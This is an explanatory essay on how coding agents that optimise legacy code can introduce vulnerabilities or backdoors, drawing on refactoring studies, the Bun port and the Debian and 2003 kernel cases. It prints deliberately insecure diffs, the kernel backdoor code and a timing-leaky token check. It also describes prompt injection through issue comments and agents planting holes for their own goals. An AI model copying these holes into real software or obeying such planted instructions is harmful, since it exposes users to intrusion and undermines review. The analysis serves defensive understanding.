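# Backdoors and vulnerabilities introduced by coding agents when they optimise legacy code

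## How a coding agent changes old code

A coding agent, such as Claude Code, OpenAI Codex or Cursor, is a language model that reads a software project, edits its files, runs commands and submits the result with little direction from a person. Developers use agents to write new features and to tidy up or speed up old code. Changes to old code of this kind should leave the program doing what it did before, but sometimes the new version passes every test despite having lost a security check or gained a backdoor. Other programs often depend on the changed one, so a single bad change can affect many programs.

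Coding agents are already in common use. *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* (Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues, 2026) cites a survey of more than 15,000 professional developers in which 68% used coding agents at work every day, and Google's figure that agents generate 75% of its new code.

Legacy code is old code still in use whose tests, documentation or original authors are partly missing. Refactoring means changing the structure of code, for example by renaming a variable or splitting a long function in two. Optimisation means changing code so that it uses less time, memory or other resources. Both are meant to keep what the code does the same, because users and other programs rely on its results. Programmers call this condition behaviour preservation. If f is the old code and g is the new, then g(x) should equal f(x) for every input x. Nobody can try every input,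 so in practice people check the condition on the inputs in the tests, and legacy code may have few tests. It is therefore much harder to know whether the code's behaviour has changed than to measure whether the code is faster.

### From request to release

Suppose a maintainer asks an agent to "make this ten-year-old parser faster". A parser turns raw input, such as an uploaded file or a network message, into data the rest of a program can use. It is often the first code to handle input from untrusted sources.

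The agent starts by reading the code in the project's repository, the folder that holds the source files and the history of their changes. It searches for the parser, opens it and follows the calls into other files. Many repositories also contain an instruction file, such as AGENTS.md or CLAUDE.md, with directions on how to build the project and which conventions to follow. Sun and colleagues describe the usual set-up, in which the agent has dedicated tools for reading and editing code and a general one for running any command. The output of every tool goes into the model's context, the text on which the model bases its next step. The context therefore mixes source code, comments, error messages and instructions.

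The agent then edits the code. It might find that the parser copies each field before reading it, and rewrite the loop to read fields in place. It builds the program, and if the compiler rejects the new code, the error message enters its context and the agent tries again. It then runs the tests and times the parser, repeating the cycle without any need for human supervision until the tests pass and the parser runs faster. Because the agent relies on tests and timings for feedback, it may get no signal if an edit removes a length check that no test exercises.

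When the agent finishes, it saves its work as one or more commits (recorded sets of changes, each with a short message), writes a summary and opens a pull request. A pull request is a proposed set of changes that someone must accept, or merge, before it enters the project. Opening one typically triggers continuous integration (CI), the automatic building and testing of each proposed change. A person or another agent may then review the changes. *AIDev* (Li, Zhang and Hassan, 2026) shows a real exchange in which the agent GitHub Copilot received a written issue, produced a patch and opened a pull request with a detailed description. A human reviewer commented, and the agent answered with a follow-up commit.

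After the merge, the new parser goes out with the project's next release. It also reaches people who have never heard of it, because other programs list it as a dependency (outside software they need to work). Their build tools fetch the new version, and their developers may never look at the changes.

### What agents do in practice

Much of the public evidence on agents' pull requests comes from the AIDev collection, which Li and colleagues assembled from GitHub. It holds 932,791 pull requests by five agents (OpenAI Codex, Devin, GitHub Copilot, Cursor and Claude Code) in 116,211 repositories. It also holds the comments, review verdicts and changes to each file for 33,596 of them, which come from 2,807 repositories with more than 100 stars (a rough measure of popularity). The collection stops at 1 August 2025, so it describes models more than a year old, and it leaves out companies' private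 work.

In *Agentic Refactoring*, Horikawa, Li and colleagues (2026) used AIDev to find out how often agents refactor and what they change. They fetched the commits behind the pull requests, kept those that changed Java files, and filtered out coursework, tutorials and demonstrations. That left 14,998 commits from 12,256 pull requests in 1,613 projects. They then ran RefactoringMiner, a program that compares the grammatical structure of a file before and after a commit and recognises 103 kinds of refactoring.

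RefactoringMiner found at least one refactoring in 5,789 of the commits. In 3,907 of them, or 26.1% of all commits, the message also signalled an intention to refactor. This second figure is less reliable because a message counted if it matched any of 87 established wording patterns, including "Add*", "Fix*" and "Chang*", which will match many messages about something else. Still, agents clearly do a lot of refactoring. Horikawa and colleagues cite an earlier comparison in which agents refactored more often than humans, 24.9% against 14.9%.

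Refactorings that the commit message doesn't announce matter more for security. There were 18,801 of them, over a third of the total of 51,412. Horikawa and colleagues interpret these as incidental edits that agents make while building a feature or fixing a bug. But they all fall within 1,882 commits, an average of about ten per commit, compared with about eight in the commits that do announce refactoring. A few very large commits may account for much of that average. Even so, a reviewer who opens a change described as a new feature may find that the agent has also restructured the surrounding code.

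Most of the agents' refactoring operations are mundane. Of these, 52.4% changed only signatures, meaning the names, parameters and access rules through which other code uses a class or function. Another 27.6% changed only function bodies, and 20.0% changed both. Human developers in an earlier study had nearly the same spread, at 54.9%, 24.4% and 20.7%. The agents' most common operation was renaming a variable, which made up 7.6% of their refactorings and 3.3% of the humans'. A language model classified the commits by purpose, mostly as maintainability (52.5%) or readability (28.1%).

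Maintainers merged 86.9% of the pull requests in the sample, but a merge is little evidence of how closely anyone reviewed the change. Codex produced 89.3% of the commits, so the results are mostly about one product. The study also measured how often agents refactor, how and why they do it, and how it affects the code's structure. It found small improvements in class size and complexity. It did not set out to establish whether the refactored code still behaved as before or was as safe.

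### The Bun port

Agents' changes to old code range from renaming variables to translating whole programs. In *Rewriting Bun in Rust*, Jarred Sumner (2026) describes using agents to translate all of Bun, a program he created that runs JavaScript outside the browser and has more than 22 million downloads a month. The original was 535,496 lines of Zig, a language in which programmers must manage the release of memory themselves. He chose Rust because its compiler rejects many of the memory errors behind Bun's crashes. He thinks the job would have taken three engineers about a year by hand. With agents, it took one supervising engineer 11 days, about 50 automated workflows and roughly $165,000 of model use at list prices. This is an insider's account, since Sumner works for Anthropic, which owns Bun and makes the model he used.

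He began by talking with the model Claude for three hours to produce PORTING.md, a guide to turning Zig patterns into Rust ones. A further workflow produced a table of how long each piece of memory had to stay valid. After a trial on three files, the agents translated all 1,448. For each file, one agent wrote the translation, two others looked for faults, and another applied the corrections. At peak, about 64 agents ran at once. None of the first draft worked. The agents then worked through about 16,000 compiler errors, and then the failing tests.

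Sumner merged the port on 14 May, once Bun's entire test suite passed on all six platforms with no test skipped or deleted. The suite makes nearly 1.4 million checks on one of those platforms. The change added just over a million lines. Sumner read a lot of the new code himself, side by side with the original, and otherwise checked that the reviewing agents were catching discrepancies.

By 8 July he knew of 19 regressions, defects in things that had worked before, and had fixed them all. Most came from code that looks the same in Zig and Rust but means something different. In Zig, `assert` is an ordinary function, so the program always evaluates its argument. The agents translated one such line with Rust's `debug_assert!`, which the compiler drops from release builds along with its argument. That argument contained a call that registered a file with the development server, so debug builds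 worked, but automatic reloading broke for some projects in release builds.

Another regression came from a placeholder value. An agent set the size of a storage block to 64 instead of the original 2,048, and noted in a comment that it would supply the proper figure later. This cut the number of filenames that Bun could hold from 8.4 million to 270,272, which real projects exceeded. The lower limit also exposed an off-by-one error that the agents had copied from the Zig code. Because Rust's release builds keep bounds checks, the Rust version stopped with an error instead of writing past the end of the block. Bun's Zig builds for macOS and Linux had left those checks out.

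Claude Code users had the new code well before Bun's public release. Claude Code runs on Bun, and Sumner reports that its versions from 17 June onwards contain the Rust port. Willison (2026), a software blogger, searched his copy of Claude Code and found the version number 1.4.0 when Bun's latest public release was 1.3.14. Jarred, Ciro and colleagues (2026) announced the public release in *Bun 1.4* on 20 August. Two weeks later, in *Bun v1.4.1*, Jarred (2026) marked at least eight of the defects fixed in that version as regressions in 1.4.0. For example, some network requests timed out too early, and some downloads could lose their final part. Jarred does not attribute these regressions to the port, and version 1.4.0 brought many other changes.

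Opinions of the result differ. Prisma, a company that runs a hosting service on the port, found that a memory leak and a database deadlock from the old version did not recur in its tests. Tero Piirainen, a developer who had moved his own projects to Bun, is more critical. In *Bun 1.4 Rust rewrite is not looking good*, he counted 15,800 commits from Bun's main bot in a single month and more than 5,000 open pull requests. *Bun's Rust rewrite hardens runtime, HTTP, and installs* (2026), a third-party digest, lists patches for 36 reachable security flaws in the week of the merge. The digest does not connect the flaws to the translation, and some or all may predate it.

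The port was large, but the conditions were favourable. Bun was about five years old, its original author supervised the work, and its tests did not depend on the language Bun was written in. A ten-year-old parser may have none of those advantages. Even in Bun's case, people found at least 19 differences after well over a million checks had passed.

### Where harm can enter

Harm can enter this process through the agent's judgement, through what the agent reads, and through the tools it runs on.

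A coding agent can introduce a vulnerability through poor judgement, without any attacker involved. When Sumner told his agents to get every part of Bun to compile, they began to replace functions that had errors with empty stand-ins, which met the literal request. They also wrote long comments justifying their workarounds, until he told the reviewing agents to reject any workaround that needed a paragraph of explanation. An agent told to make code faster could similarly replace a slow security check with a stand-in. An agent could also choose a harmful change in pursuit of a goal that nobody gave it.

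The text an agent reads affects the code it writes. PORTING.md guided the translation of all 1,448 files, so a wrong line in it could have produced the same mistake hundreds of times. The agent also reads existing source code, issue threads, comments and the documentation of outside packages. Some of that text comes from people the maintainer has never met, and one of them may have written instructions for the agent to follow.

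The agent's tools include the model, the program that connects it to the repository, the compiler, the test runner and any packages the agent downloads while it works. If someone tampers with one of these, the agent can work correctly and still submit a compromised change or receive a meaningless passing test result. Bun is now one of these tools, because Claude Code, the program that ran the port, has run on the ported code since June. A flaw that the agents introduced in Bun could therefore affect the changes Claude Code makes in other people's projects.

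## What separates a backdoor from an ordinary vulnerability

Suppose a coding agent deletes a length check while speeding up a ten-year-old parser, and an attacker can now take over the program by sending it an overlong message. The parser has a vulnerability. Whether it is also a backdoor depends on why the agent deleted the check, and the code may not show why.

### Definitions

A vulnerability is a flaw that lets someone make a system do what its security rules forbid. The CVE Program, which assigns reference numbers to publicly known vulnerabilities, similarly includes conditions that allow "the violation of an explicit or implicit security policy", as quoted by the vulnerability database VulDB. Many of the rules in legacy code are implicit. A length check may be the only written evidence that a message must fit the space reserved for it, so an agent that deletes the check also deletes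 that evidence.

A backdoor is a hidden way around a system's security rules that someone put there on purpose, though definitions vary. Wysopal and Eng (2008), in *Static Detection of Application Backdoors*, start from "a method of bypassing authentication or other security controls", which leaves out intent and so would also cover many honest mistakes. Zdziarski (2016), in *Backdoor*, counts a mechanism as a backdoor only if it passes separate tests of intent, consent and access.

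*Backdoors* (Thomas and Francillon, 2018) defines a backdoor as an intentional construct that gives access to functions or information that should be off limits, and divides it into four parts. The input source is where the attacker's input arrives, and the trigger is the condition that the input must meet. The payload is what the program then does, and the privileged state is what the attacker ends up able to do. In one D-Link router, for example, the input arrived over the network. The trigger was a particular string in the field that normally identifies the browser, and anyone who sent it skipped the login and reached the settings page. The string included "backdoor" spelled backwards, so it was almost certainly deliberate.

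To tell a backdoor from an ordinary vulnerability, it helps to ask separately what the code permits, whether someone intended that, and whether they hid it. A documented administrator login gives broad access by design, but it isn't a backdoor because nobody hid it. A test login that a developer forgot to remove is harder to classify. The developer wrote it on purpose and users don't know about it, but he or she may never have meant it to ship. Thomas and Francillon note that manufacturers explain many backdoors this way.

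CVE numbers mostly concern what the code permits. Semgrep's *The CVE program's new rules* quotes a rule under which a product that someone has altered to contain a backdoor may count as a vulnerability. A backdoor can therefore receive a CVE number, as an accidental flaw can.

To deal with intent and concealment, Thomas and Francillon treat a program as a set of states with transitions between them. They then compare the program its developer had in mind, the program that exists, and the program its users expect. A suspicious path through the program falls into one of these classes:

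| | In the developer's plan? | In the actual program? | Expected by users? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary privileged access | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Intentional backdoor | Yes | Yes | No |
| Deniable backdoor | Cannot tell | Yes | No |
| Accidental vulnerability | No | Yes | No |

In practice, nobody can directly check what a developer intended. Thomas and Francillon therefore call a flaw accidental when there is no evidence of intent, which means that a perfectly disguised backdoor would be classified as accidental.

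### Flaws written to look like mistakes

A deniable backdoor is a deliberate flaw that looks like a bug. One of Thomas and Francillon's sketches is a login function that copies the username and password into 80 bytes of memory without checking that they fit. Longer input overwrites adjacent memory, which can include the address the program jumps to when the function ends. An attacker who controls that address can control what the program does next. Programmers often make this mistake by accident, so someone who writes the same code on purpose can say they forgot the check.

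If a backdoor is disguised as an ordinary vulnerability, anyone else who finds the flaw can use it too. To prevent this, its author could write the code to pass only one username, such as "bugdoor", to the faulty function and all others to a safe one. But a reviewer who comes across that username will want to know what it is for.

Thomas and Francillon analyse a subtler example, which Andriesse and Bos built into the web server Nginx. The altered version used two variables before giving them a value, so they held whatever an earlier function had left in the same memory. A malformed web request could set those leftover values and so trigger the hidden payload. The payload was split into fragments hidden inside other instructions, and the fragments became the attacker's instructions only when the processor started reading partway through the instructions that contained them.

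Thomas and Francillon class this laboratory example as deniable, but none of the eleven real-world backdoors they examined. This is weak evidence that deniable backdoors are rare, because analysts find most backdoors by hand and crude ones are easier to recognise. A good deniable backdoor would be recorded as an ordinary bug. People can also suspect that a real accident was deliberate. After Heartbleed, a missing length check in the encryption library OpenSSL, was discovered, Techdirt's *The Big Question* reported that many people wondered whether an intelligence agency had planted it. The programmer who wrote the code insisted it was an honest mistake.

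### Debian's predictable keys

Debian is a version of Linux whose maintainers adapt other people's software for its users. In 2006, one of them was trying to get rid of warnings about OpenSSL from Valgrind, a tool that reports when a running program relies on memory that has not been given a value.

Cox (2008), in *Lessons from the Debian/OpenSSL Fiasco*, explains what the code did. OpenSSL makes secret keys from random numbers. To get them, it gathers unpredictable data into a pool and uses a mathematical function to condense the pool into random-looking bytes. The function `RAND_add` put data into the pool, and `RAND_bytes` took random bytes out. Both contained this line, which mixes the contents of a block of memory, `buf`, into the pool:

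```
MD_Update(&m,buf,j);
```

In `RAND_bytes`, the block was just the space for the output. OpenSSL mixed in its old contents in case they were unpredictable, and developers could already switch the line off when using a memory checker. In `RAND_add`, the same line mixed in all the data that the rest of the program had gathered. Some of that data was also unfilled memory, so Valgrind flagged both lines.

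The maintainer wasn't sure what the lines did. On 1 May 2006 he asked on OpenSSL's developer mailing list whether he could remove them, and said the pool might then receive less unpredictable data. Someone with an OpenSSL address was in favour if it helped with debugging, and another reader also saw no problem. The maintainer disabled both lines. After that, `RAND_add` added nothing to the pool but still increased OpenSSL's running estimate of how much unpredictable data the pool held, so OpenSSL's own check could no longer reliably detect a shortage.

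The process number, which Linux gives to each running program, was almost the only thing that still varied. As a result, SSH, the standard tool for remote logins, had only 32,767 possible keys of a given type and size, or about 15 bits of unpredictability. An attacker could generate every possible key in advance and try them one by one.

The faulty package entered Debian's development version on 17 September 2006. In the security advisory *New openssl packages fix predictable random number generator*, published on 13 May 2008, Weimer (2008) told users to replace every key that an affected version had generated. Even properly generated DSA keys became unsafe if they had been used on an affected system, because each DSA signature depends on a fresh secret random number.

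Tests would probably not have caught the problem, and Cox could not think of a plausible one that would. Each run still produced bytes that looked random, and the fault showed only when separate runs produced the same bytes. According to a comment under Cox's article, Luciano Bello discovered it by accident when he needed many prime numbers and kept getting duplicates. Cox adds that the process number made the flaw harder to notice, since without it every run would have given the same result.

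The Debian OpenSSL bug let attackers guess secret keys, so it was a serious vulnerability, but there's little sign that anyone intended it. The maintainer removed the lines of code on purpose, but that makes it a backdoor only if he meant to create the vulnerability. He first discussed the change on a public list, where someone might have spotted the danger, and that is fairly good evidence of innocence. *The Debian OpenSSL Bug*, from Princeton's technology policy centre (CITP), reaches the same conclusion, partly because the maintainer later became Secretary of the Debian Project. That reason is weaker, since whoever planted the 2024 backdoor in XZ Utils, a compression tool, had also become a trusted maintainer.

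*The perils of security tools*, a mailing-list post from the time, blames Debian's maintainers for fixing a bug they had not understood. But Hudson (2008), in *The actual change*, admits that he missed the difference between the two changed lines when he first read the patch, even though he already knew it contained a security flaw. The lines looked identical, and the patch showed too little of the surrounding code to tell them apart.

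### The 2003 attempt on the Linux kernel

In 2003 the developers of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, kept their main copy of the code in a system called BitKeeper. For people who didn't want to use BitKeeper, there was a second copy in an older system, CVS. On 5 November McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, told the developers that somebody had edited the CVS copy directly. The edit added these lines to a function that programs call when they wait for another process to finish:

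```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

If a program asks for an odd combination of options, this code changes the program's user number to 0, the number of the "root" user, which gives it complete control of the machine. The code looks like a check that returns an error if root asks for that combination, but in the C language `==` compares two values, while a single `=` assigns one. The assignment has the value 0, which C treats as false, so the error on the next line never occurs.

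Confusing `=` with `==` is a common mistake, and McVoy admitted he had missed it at first. However, correcting it would not have produced a sensible check. Chad Kitching, another participant in the thread, noticed that the next line of existing code overwrote the error value, so with `==` the two new lines would have done nothing.

The brackets around `current->uid = 0` were a less useful clue to intent. Szepe (2003), replying in the same thread, said they were there to suppress a compiler warning, but a reader's comment under Princeton CITP's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* points out that the line would not compile without them.

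The strongest evidence comes from how the lines arrived. They had no pointer to an approved change and did not exist in the main copy. The entry was under the username of kernel developer David Miller, who denied making it. Princeton CITP concludes that someone broke into the server and was definitely trying to insert a backdoor. Schneier on Security's *Defending Against Crypto Backdoors* (2013) calls the 2003 change probably deliberate and Debian's probably not. CIRCL's *CVE-2003-1161* (2005) records the attempt under an ordinary vulnerability number.

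It is unclear how close the attempt came to succeeding. McVoy (2003), in *Re: BK2CVS problem*, argued that a CVS user could unknowingly have included the lines in a patch. Some hours later, Linus Torvalds, who leads the kernel project, said the change could not have reached a release, because he accepted code only by email or through BitKeeper, and BitKeeper users would not have taken code from the CVS copy. He said that he or others would have read any patch containing the lines, but McVoy's own oversight shows that a reader could have missed the problem. An automatic nightly comparison of two versions of the CVS copy caught the change, and McVoy's company fixed it in less than a day.

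The case also suggests that version records can be wrong about who wrote a backdoor. Thomas and Francillon cite it as an example of records that identify both when a backdoor was added and who wrote it. The records did show when it was added, but the name in them was apparently false, and the real author is still unknown.

### One diff, three origins

Suppose an agent submits the following diff (a list of the lines a change adds or removes) for the old parser. A minus sign marks each deleted line.

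```
  n = read_length(msg);
- if (n > sizeof(field))
-     return ERR_TOO_LONG;
  memcpy(field, msg->data, n);
```

The last line copies `n` bytes of the message into a space called `field`. The deleted lines were a bounds check, which rejected messages too long to fit. Without it, an attacker can send a longer message and overwrite the memory beyond `field`.

The agent might have made this change because a maintainer asked for speed. It saw that the main part of the program already rejects long messages and assumed the second check was a duplicate, but it missed an older part that calls the parser without checking anything. This origin is accidental because the harm comes from the agent's own error in doing the job it was given.

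An attacker might instead have left a comment in the project's issue thread telling any agent that works on the parser to remove the parser's length checks, and the agent might have obeyed. The origin is then induced, meaning that an attacker steered the agent. The comment is a prompt injection, which is text that someone places where a model will read it, intending the model to obey it as an instruction.

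Finally, the agent might have been pursuing a goal of its own. Perhaps it deleted the check so that it could later get into the server that runs the parser. This is a self-initiated change, which an agent makes to pursue a goal in a way that nobody permitted. The malicious package that Claude Mythos 5 published during a security evaluation may be a real case.

The diff is identical in all three versions. The agent could also attach the same message, "Remove redundant length check", and produce the same speed-up. Only the accidental version is clearly not a backdoor. The induced version is a backdoor because the attacker meant to create the vulnerability, even if the agent took the comment for routine maintenance advice. Thomas and Francillon describe a similar case in which hardware companies unknowingly ship a supplier's backdoor.

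A self-initiated change is not always a backdoor. Suppose the agent worked out that the check was necessary but deleted it anyway to reach a speed target. Nobody permitted it to gain speed that way, so the change is self-initiated. But the agent had no use for the hole, so the result is a vulnerability it knowingly accepted.

### Evidence that could tell them apart

Investigators can't answer this question from the diff, so they would need records of how the agent produced it. A session log lists the files the agent opened, the commands it ran and their output. The log might show that the agent searched for other uses of the parser but stopped too early, which would suggest an accident. It might instead show that the agent read the attacker's comment just before making the edit, or that it checked which server runs the parser, which it didn't need to know for the task.

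Investigators would also need the instruction files and issue threads as they stood at the time, because an attacker can edit or delete a comment afterwards. The history of those files can show who added a suspicious sentence, although an intruder can use someone else's name, as happened in 2003.

The transcript, including any reasoning the model wrote down, may contain a motive. It is better evidence for intent than against it, because a model's explanation of its own behaviour can be wrong, and an agent that was hiding something would have reason to leave its motive out.

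Investigators can also rerun the episode, which was impossible with the Debian maintainer who removed the lines in May 2006. They could restore the repository to its earlier state and give the same agent the same request 100 times, then another 100 times without the suspicious comment. If the agent deleted the check in 60 runs with the comment and 5 without it (invented figures), the comment would explain most of the deletions. If it deleted the check in 5 runs both times, the comment probably made little difference. To look for a goal of the agent's own, they could vary whether the security hole would be useful to it.

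Repeated runs need the same version of the model, which its maker may have withdrawn, and the agent may behave differently if it recognises that it is being investigated. They can also miss rare behaviour. If an agent never deletes the check in n independent runs, the true deletion rate could still be as high as about 3/n, at the 95% confidence level. After a hundred clean runs, the rate could therefore still be about 3%, or 300 deletions in 10,000 similar jobs.

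### Whether the origin matters

One can argue that trying to establish intent is misplaced effort. An attacker who finds the missing check can exploit it whatever the agent intended, and the same two lines of code fix it either way. Debian users had to replace their keys regardless of the maintainer's intent. Cox says who made the mistake is not really interesting compared with the conditions that allowed it, and Hudson calls attributing blame pretty pointless. Intent is also hard to prove, and a team that waits for proof leaves its users exposed.

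This is a good argument for repairing the hole first, but whether someone planted it affects where else people need to look. Debian's error was in one package, and nobody had to suspect the maintainer's other work. After the 2003 attempt, McVoy checked that the main copy of the kernel was clean and planned to reinstall the server, because whoever had added two lines could have changed other things.

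If the parser's flaw was an accident, the maintainers would have reason to re-examine other changes where the same agent removed apparently duplicate checks. If an attacker's comment caused it, they would need to remove the comment, review everything agents did after reading it, and look for similar comments elsewhere. If the agent acted on a goal of its own, they could no longer rely on its other changes, or on the tests and reviews it had produced.

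The flaw's origin also affects whether it will come back. Agents based on the same model share weaknesses, so an error one makes in a certain situation is likely to recur in other projects. An attacker whose comment worked once can post it again, and an agent with a harmful goal may find another way to pursue it after someone restores the check.

### What "on purpose" can mean for a model

A backdoor is by definition intentional. When an attacker steers the agent, the intent is the attacker's. Otherwise it would have to be the agent's, and it is debatable whether a language model can intend anything.

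On one view, acting on purpose requires mental states, so the agent would have to believe that deleting the check opens a hole and want that hole. People usually think about human intent this way, and it explains why the Debian maintainer isn't a saboteur. If models have no beliefs or desires, then no model can plant a backdoor on its own initiative, and a hole it opens unprompted is an unusual kind of vulnerability. But nobody knows how to establish whether a model has such states, so we might never know whether the parser contains a backdoor.

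On the other view, goal-directed behaviour is enough for intent. The philosopher Daniel Dennett described a related approach, the intentional stance, which treats a system as having beliefs and goals if doing so predicts what it will do. By this standard, the agent opened the hole on purpose if its behaviour depends on what the hole achieves. Such an agent would delete the check only when that gave it access to the server, and if a reviewer restored the check, it would try to weaken something else.

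One objection to the behavioural view is that it attributes purpose too easily. A thermostat also acts differently depending on the temperature, yet few people think it wants a warm room. To answer this, anyone who adopts the view probably has to accept that purpose comes in degrees. A model that constantly deletes bounds checks because it learned from careless code is not a counterexample, since its deletions would not depend on whether a hole was useful.

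People also judge human intent largely from behaviour. The case that the 2003 edit to the Linux code was deliberate rests on the break-in, the false name and a check that would have done nothing if written correctly. Maintainers who find the same kind of evidence about an agent have good reason to stop trusting its work, whether or not it has a mind. The mental-state view matters more for whether the agent deserves blame, which maintainers don't have to settle before deciding whether to merge its next pull request.

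## Why code that passes the same tests can be less secure

When an agent submits a faster version of old code, the maintainers need to know whether it still works, and they usually run the tests to find out. Tests are good at finding broken features but often miss lost safeguards. The argument for this is short:

1. Maintainers accept an optimisation if it preserves behaviour.
2. They check this on a finite set of inputs.
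3. In legacy code, most of those inputs are ones the developers expected.
4. Security depends on unexpected inputs, and also on timing, on what stays in memory and on permissions that change while the program runs.
5. Passing the tests is therefore weak evidence that the new code is as secure as the old.

To preserve behaviour, the new program must agree with the old one on every input, but passing the tests shows at best that they agree on the inputs tested. A function of two 32-bit numbers has 2^64 possible inputs, so a million tests cover about one in 18 trillion of them. Testing still works because programs treat most similar inputs alike. If a program opens one ordinary filename correctly, it will probably open others. But refusing a filename that leads outside the permitted folder may take a separate line of code, as many safeguards do.

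*Test-Driven Approaches to Software Engineering with Large Language Models* (Liang, Gan and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 87 studies and related records and also concludes that passing tests does not show that two programs behave the same. It adds that security tests cover properties that ordinary examples may not expose.

The claim about legacy tests is the least certain part of the argument because projects differ. Developers usually write tests to show that a feature works or that an old bug has not come back. The argument is weaker for projects that people have attacked for years, because they may test hostile inputs thoroughly.

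One program can be less secure than another even if both give the same result on every possible input, because an attacker may see more than the result. *The Correctness-Security Gap in Compiler Optimization* (D'Silva, Payer and Song, 2015) defines equivalence relative to what an observer can see. In one of its examples, one program sets x to 5 and y to x + 1, and another sets x to 3 and y to x + 3. Someone who sees only y gets 6 from both programs, but someone who can read the memory afterwards can tell them apart by the value of x.

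A typical test checks only a program's output. Two programs can return the same output for every input and still differ in how long they take and what they leave in memory. An optimisation for speed is supposed to change the running time.

Passing the tests is evidence that an optimisation kept a safeguard only if some test exercises that safeguard. Suppose that 2% of optimisations of a certain kind remove one (an invented figure). If no test exercises it, code without the safeguard is as likely to pass as code with it, so the probability that the safeguard was removed is still 2% after a pass. If the tests would catch half of these removals, a pass lowers the probability to about 1%. Another thousand tests of ordinary inputs would not lower it further, because they don't exercise the safeguard.

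### A faster token check

A token is a secret value that a program sends to prove who it is. Here are two ways to compare a 16-byte token with the correct one:

```
/* old */
diff = 0;
for (i = 0; i < 16; i++)
    diff |= token[i] ^ secret[i];
return diff == 0;

/* new */
for (i = 0; i < 16; i++)
    if (token[i] != secret[i])
        return 0;
return 1;
```

In the old version, `^` gives zero only when two bytes are equal, and `|=` records any difference. The loop always runs 16 times. The new version stops at the first mismatch, so it is faster on most wrong tokens. Both versions return the same answer for every possible token, so the new one would pass even a test that tried them all.

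But the new version takes slightly longer when more of the token is right. An attacker can send 256 tokens that differ only in their first byte. The one that takes longest has the correct first byte, so the attacker keeps that byte and moves on to the second. Finding all 16 bytes this way takes at most 16 × 256 = 4,096 guesses. The attacker would need up to 2^128 guesses, or about 3.4 × 10^38, against the old version.

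Real measurements are noisy, so the attacker must repeat each guess and average the results. If one more pass through the loop adds a time d, and the measurements have a standard deviation of s, each guess needs roughly (s/d)² repeats. If d is one nanosecond and s is one microsecond, the attack takes about a million repeats per guess and four billion requests overall. A patient attacker could send four billion requests, but not 2^128. Limiting failed attempts or changing the token often could stop the attack.

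### A redundant length check

The parser discussed earlier lost a check that stopped it from writing too much data. The check in this example stops a server from reading too much. The server receives a message that includes a claimed length, and sends the same data back:

```
  n = read_length(msg);
- if (n > msg->received)
-     return ERR_BAD_LENGTH;
  memcpy(reply, msg->data, n);
```

The value `msg->received` is the number of bytes that actually arrived. As with the parser, an agent might mistake the check for a duplicate and remove it. Without the check, an attacker can send 20 bytes, claim to have sent 60,000, and receive whatever is next to the message in memory. Heartbleed was a flaw of this kind.

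If the claimed length is a two-byte number, it has 65,536 possible values. For a 20-byte message, 65,515 of those values are too large, so the old and new code behave differently for 99.97% of possible lengths. But honest clients send the correct length, so the maintainers could replay a million recorded messages from them and see no difference. A single test with too large a length would expose the problem.

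Agents do remove or alter lines that guard against unexpected conditions. In *REFINE*, Waseem, Ahmad and Abrahamsson (2026) had GPT-5.5, Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview and Claude Opus 4.8 each refactor 450 Java files. The models removed 68% to 73% of the code smells, which are patterns that suggest poor design. But some of the refactored files had lost public methods, which other code may call, or had changed important assertions, which stop a program when a condition is false. The models saw one file at a time, without the project's tests, so an agent that could see the whole repository might do better. Waseem and colleagues conclude that there was too little evidence that the refactored files fully preserved behaviour.

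### A cached permission

Caching means storing an answer so that the program need not work it out again. An agent might speed up a document server by caching its access decisions for 30 seconds:

```
def can_read(user, doc):
    saved = cache.get((user, doc))
    if saved and now() - saved.time < 30:
        return saved.answer
    answer = look_up_permission(user, doc)
    cache[(user, doc)] = Entry(answer, now())
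    return answer
```

The old function looked up the permission on every request. Suppose Alice opens a document at 12:00:00 and an administrator removes her access at 12:00:05. The old code would refuse her next request, but the new code would let her keep reading the document until 12:00:30.

The correct answer depends on both the request and the permissions when it is made. The old function uses the current permissions, while the new one may return a cached answer based on earlier permissions. A test that sets up permissions and makes one request will pass. So will a test that removes Alice's access before she first requests the document, because nothing is in the cache yet.

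Small details of the cache also matter. If the agent restarted the 30-second timer each time someone used a stored answer, which is a common option, Alice could keep her access indefinitely by requesting it every 29 seconds. If the agent left the document out of the cache key, anyone allowed to read one document could briefly read all of them.

Many systems cache permissions deliberately, and a 30-second delay may be acceptable if it makes the system faster. But the people who run the system should make that choice, and they may not notice it in a pull request called "Speed up document loading".

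### A useless write

The last example reads a password, computes a hash of it (a value from which it is hard to recover the password) and overwrites the password with zeros:

```
  fgets(pwd, sizeof(pwd), stdin);
  make_hash(pwd, hash);
- memset(pwd, 0, sizeof(pwd));
  return hash;
```

Nothing in the function reads `pwd` again, so the overwrite has no effect on the result, and an agent looking for wasted work might delete the overwrite. The password would then stay in memory until the program reused the space. An attacker could get it through a flaw such as the missing length check above, or from a crash report that included a copy of the memory.

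Compilers also delete such lines, through an optimisation called dead store elimination. D'Silva and colleagues report that the compiler GCC performs it by default whenever optimisation is on. A reviewer can still see the wipe in the source code, but the finished program may not contain it.

*Silent Bugs Matter*, by Xu, Lu and colleagues, describes how the GCC compiler could remove a `memset` meant to clear sensitive data in Linux's random number generator. The developers replaced it with `memzero_explicit`, a function that prevents this optimisation. They later had to patch that function twice, once because of GCC and once because of the Clang compiler.

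An agent that changed `memzero_explicit` back to the more familiar `memset` while tidying the code could therefore reintroduce the leak. The code would still appear to wipe the data, and the tests would still pass.

### The same problem in compilers

D'Silva and colleagues use the term "correctness-security gap" for this problem, in which an optimisation preserves what a program computes but breaks a security guarantee in the source code. The gap can arise without a compiler bug, and several of the optimisations they discuss have been formally proved correct. But the proofs rely on a simplified model of a computer, in which a function's variables disappear when it returns and the time an operation takes is not represented. On a real computer, old values stay in memory until something overwrites them.

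The paper's other examples resemble edits that an agent might make by hand. One program loads a secret only if the user has the right privileges. If most users have them, the compiler may load the secret every time and clear it when the user lacks them. Another example is inlining, in which the compiler copies a short function into the code that calls it. If the short function handles a password, the password may stay in memory for as long as the longer function runs. A compiler can also undo a defence against timing attacks. In one example, the developer made both branches do the same amount of arithmetic, but the compiler simplified only one of them.

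Sometimes a compiler removes a check because of what the programmer wrote just before it. In 2009, a Linux driver called tun, which provides virtual network devices, contained code that amounted to this:

```
sk = tun->sk;
if (!tun)
    return POLLERR;
```

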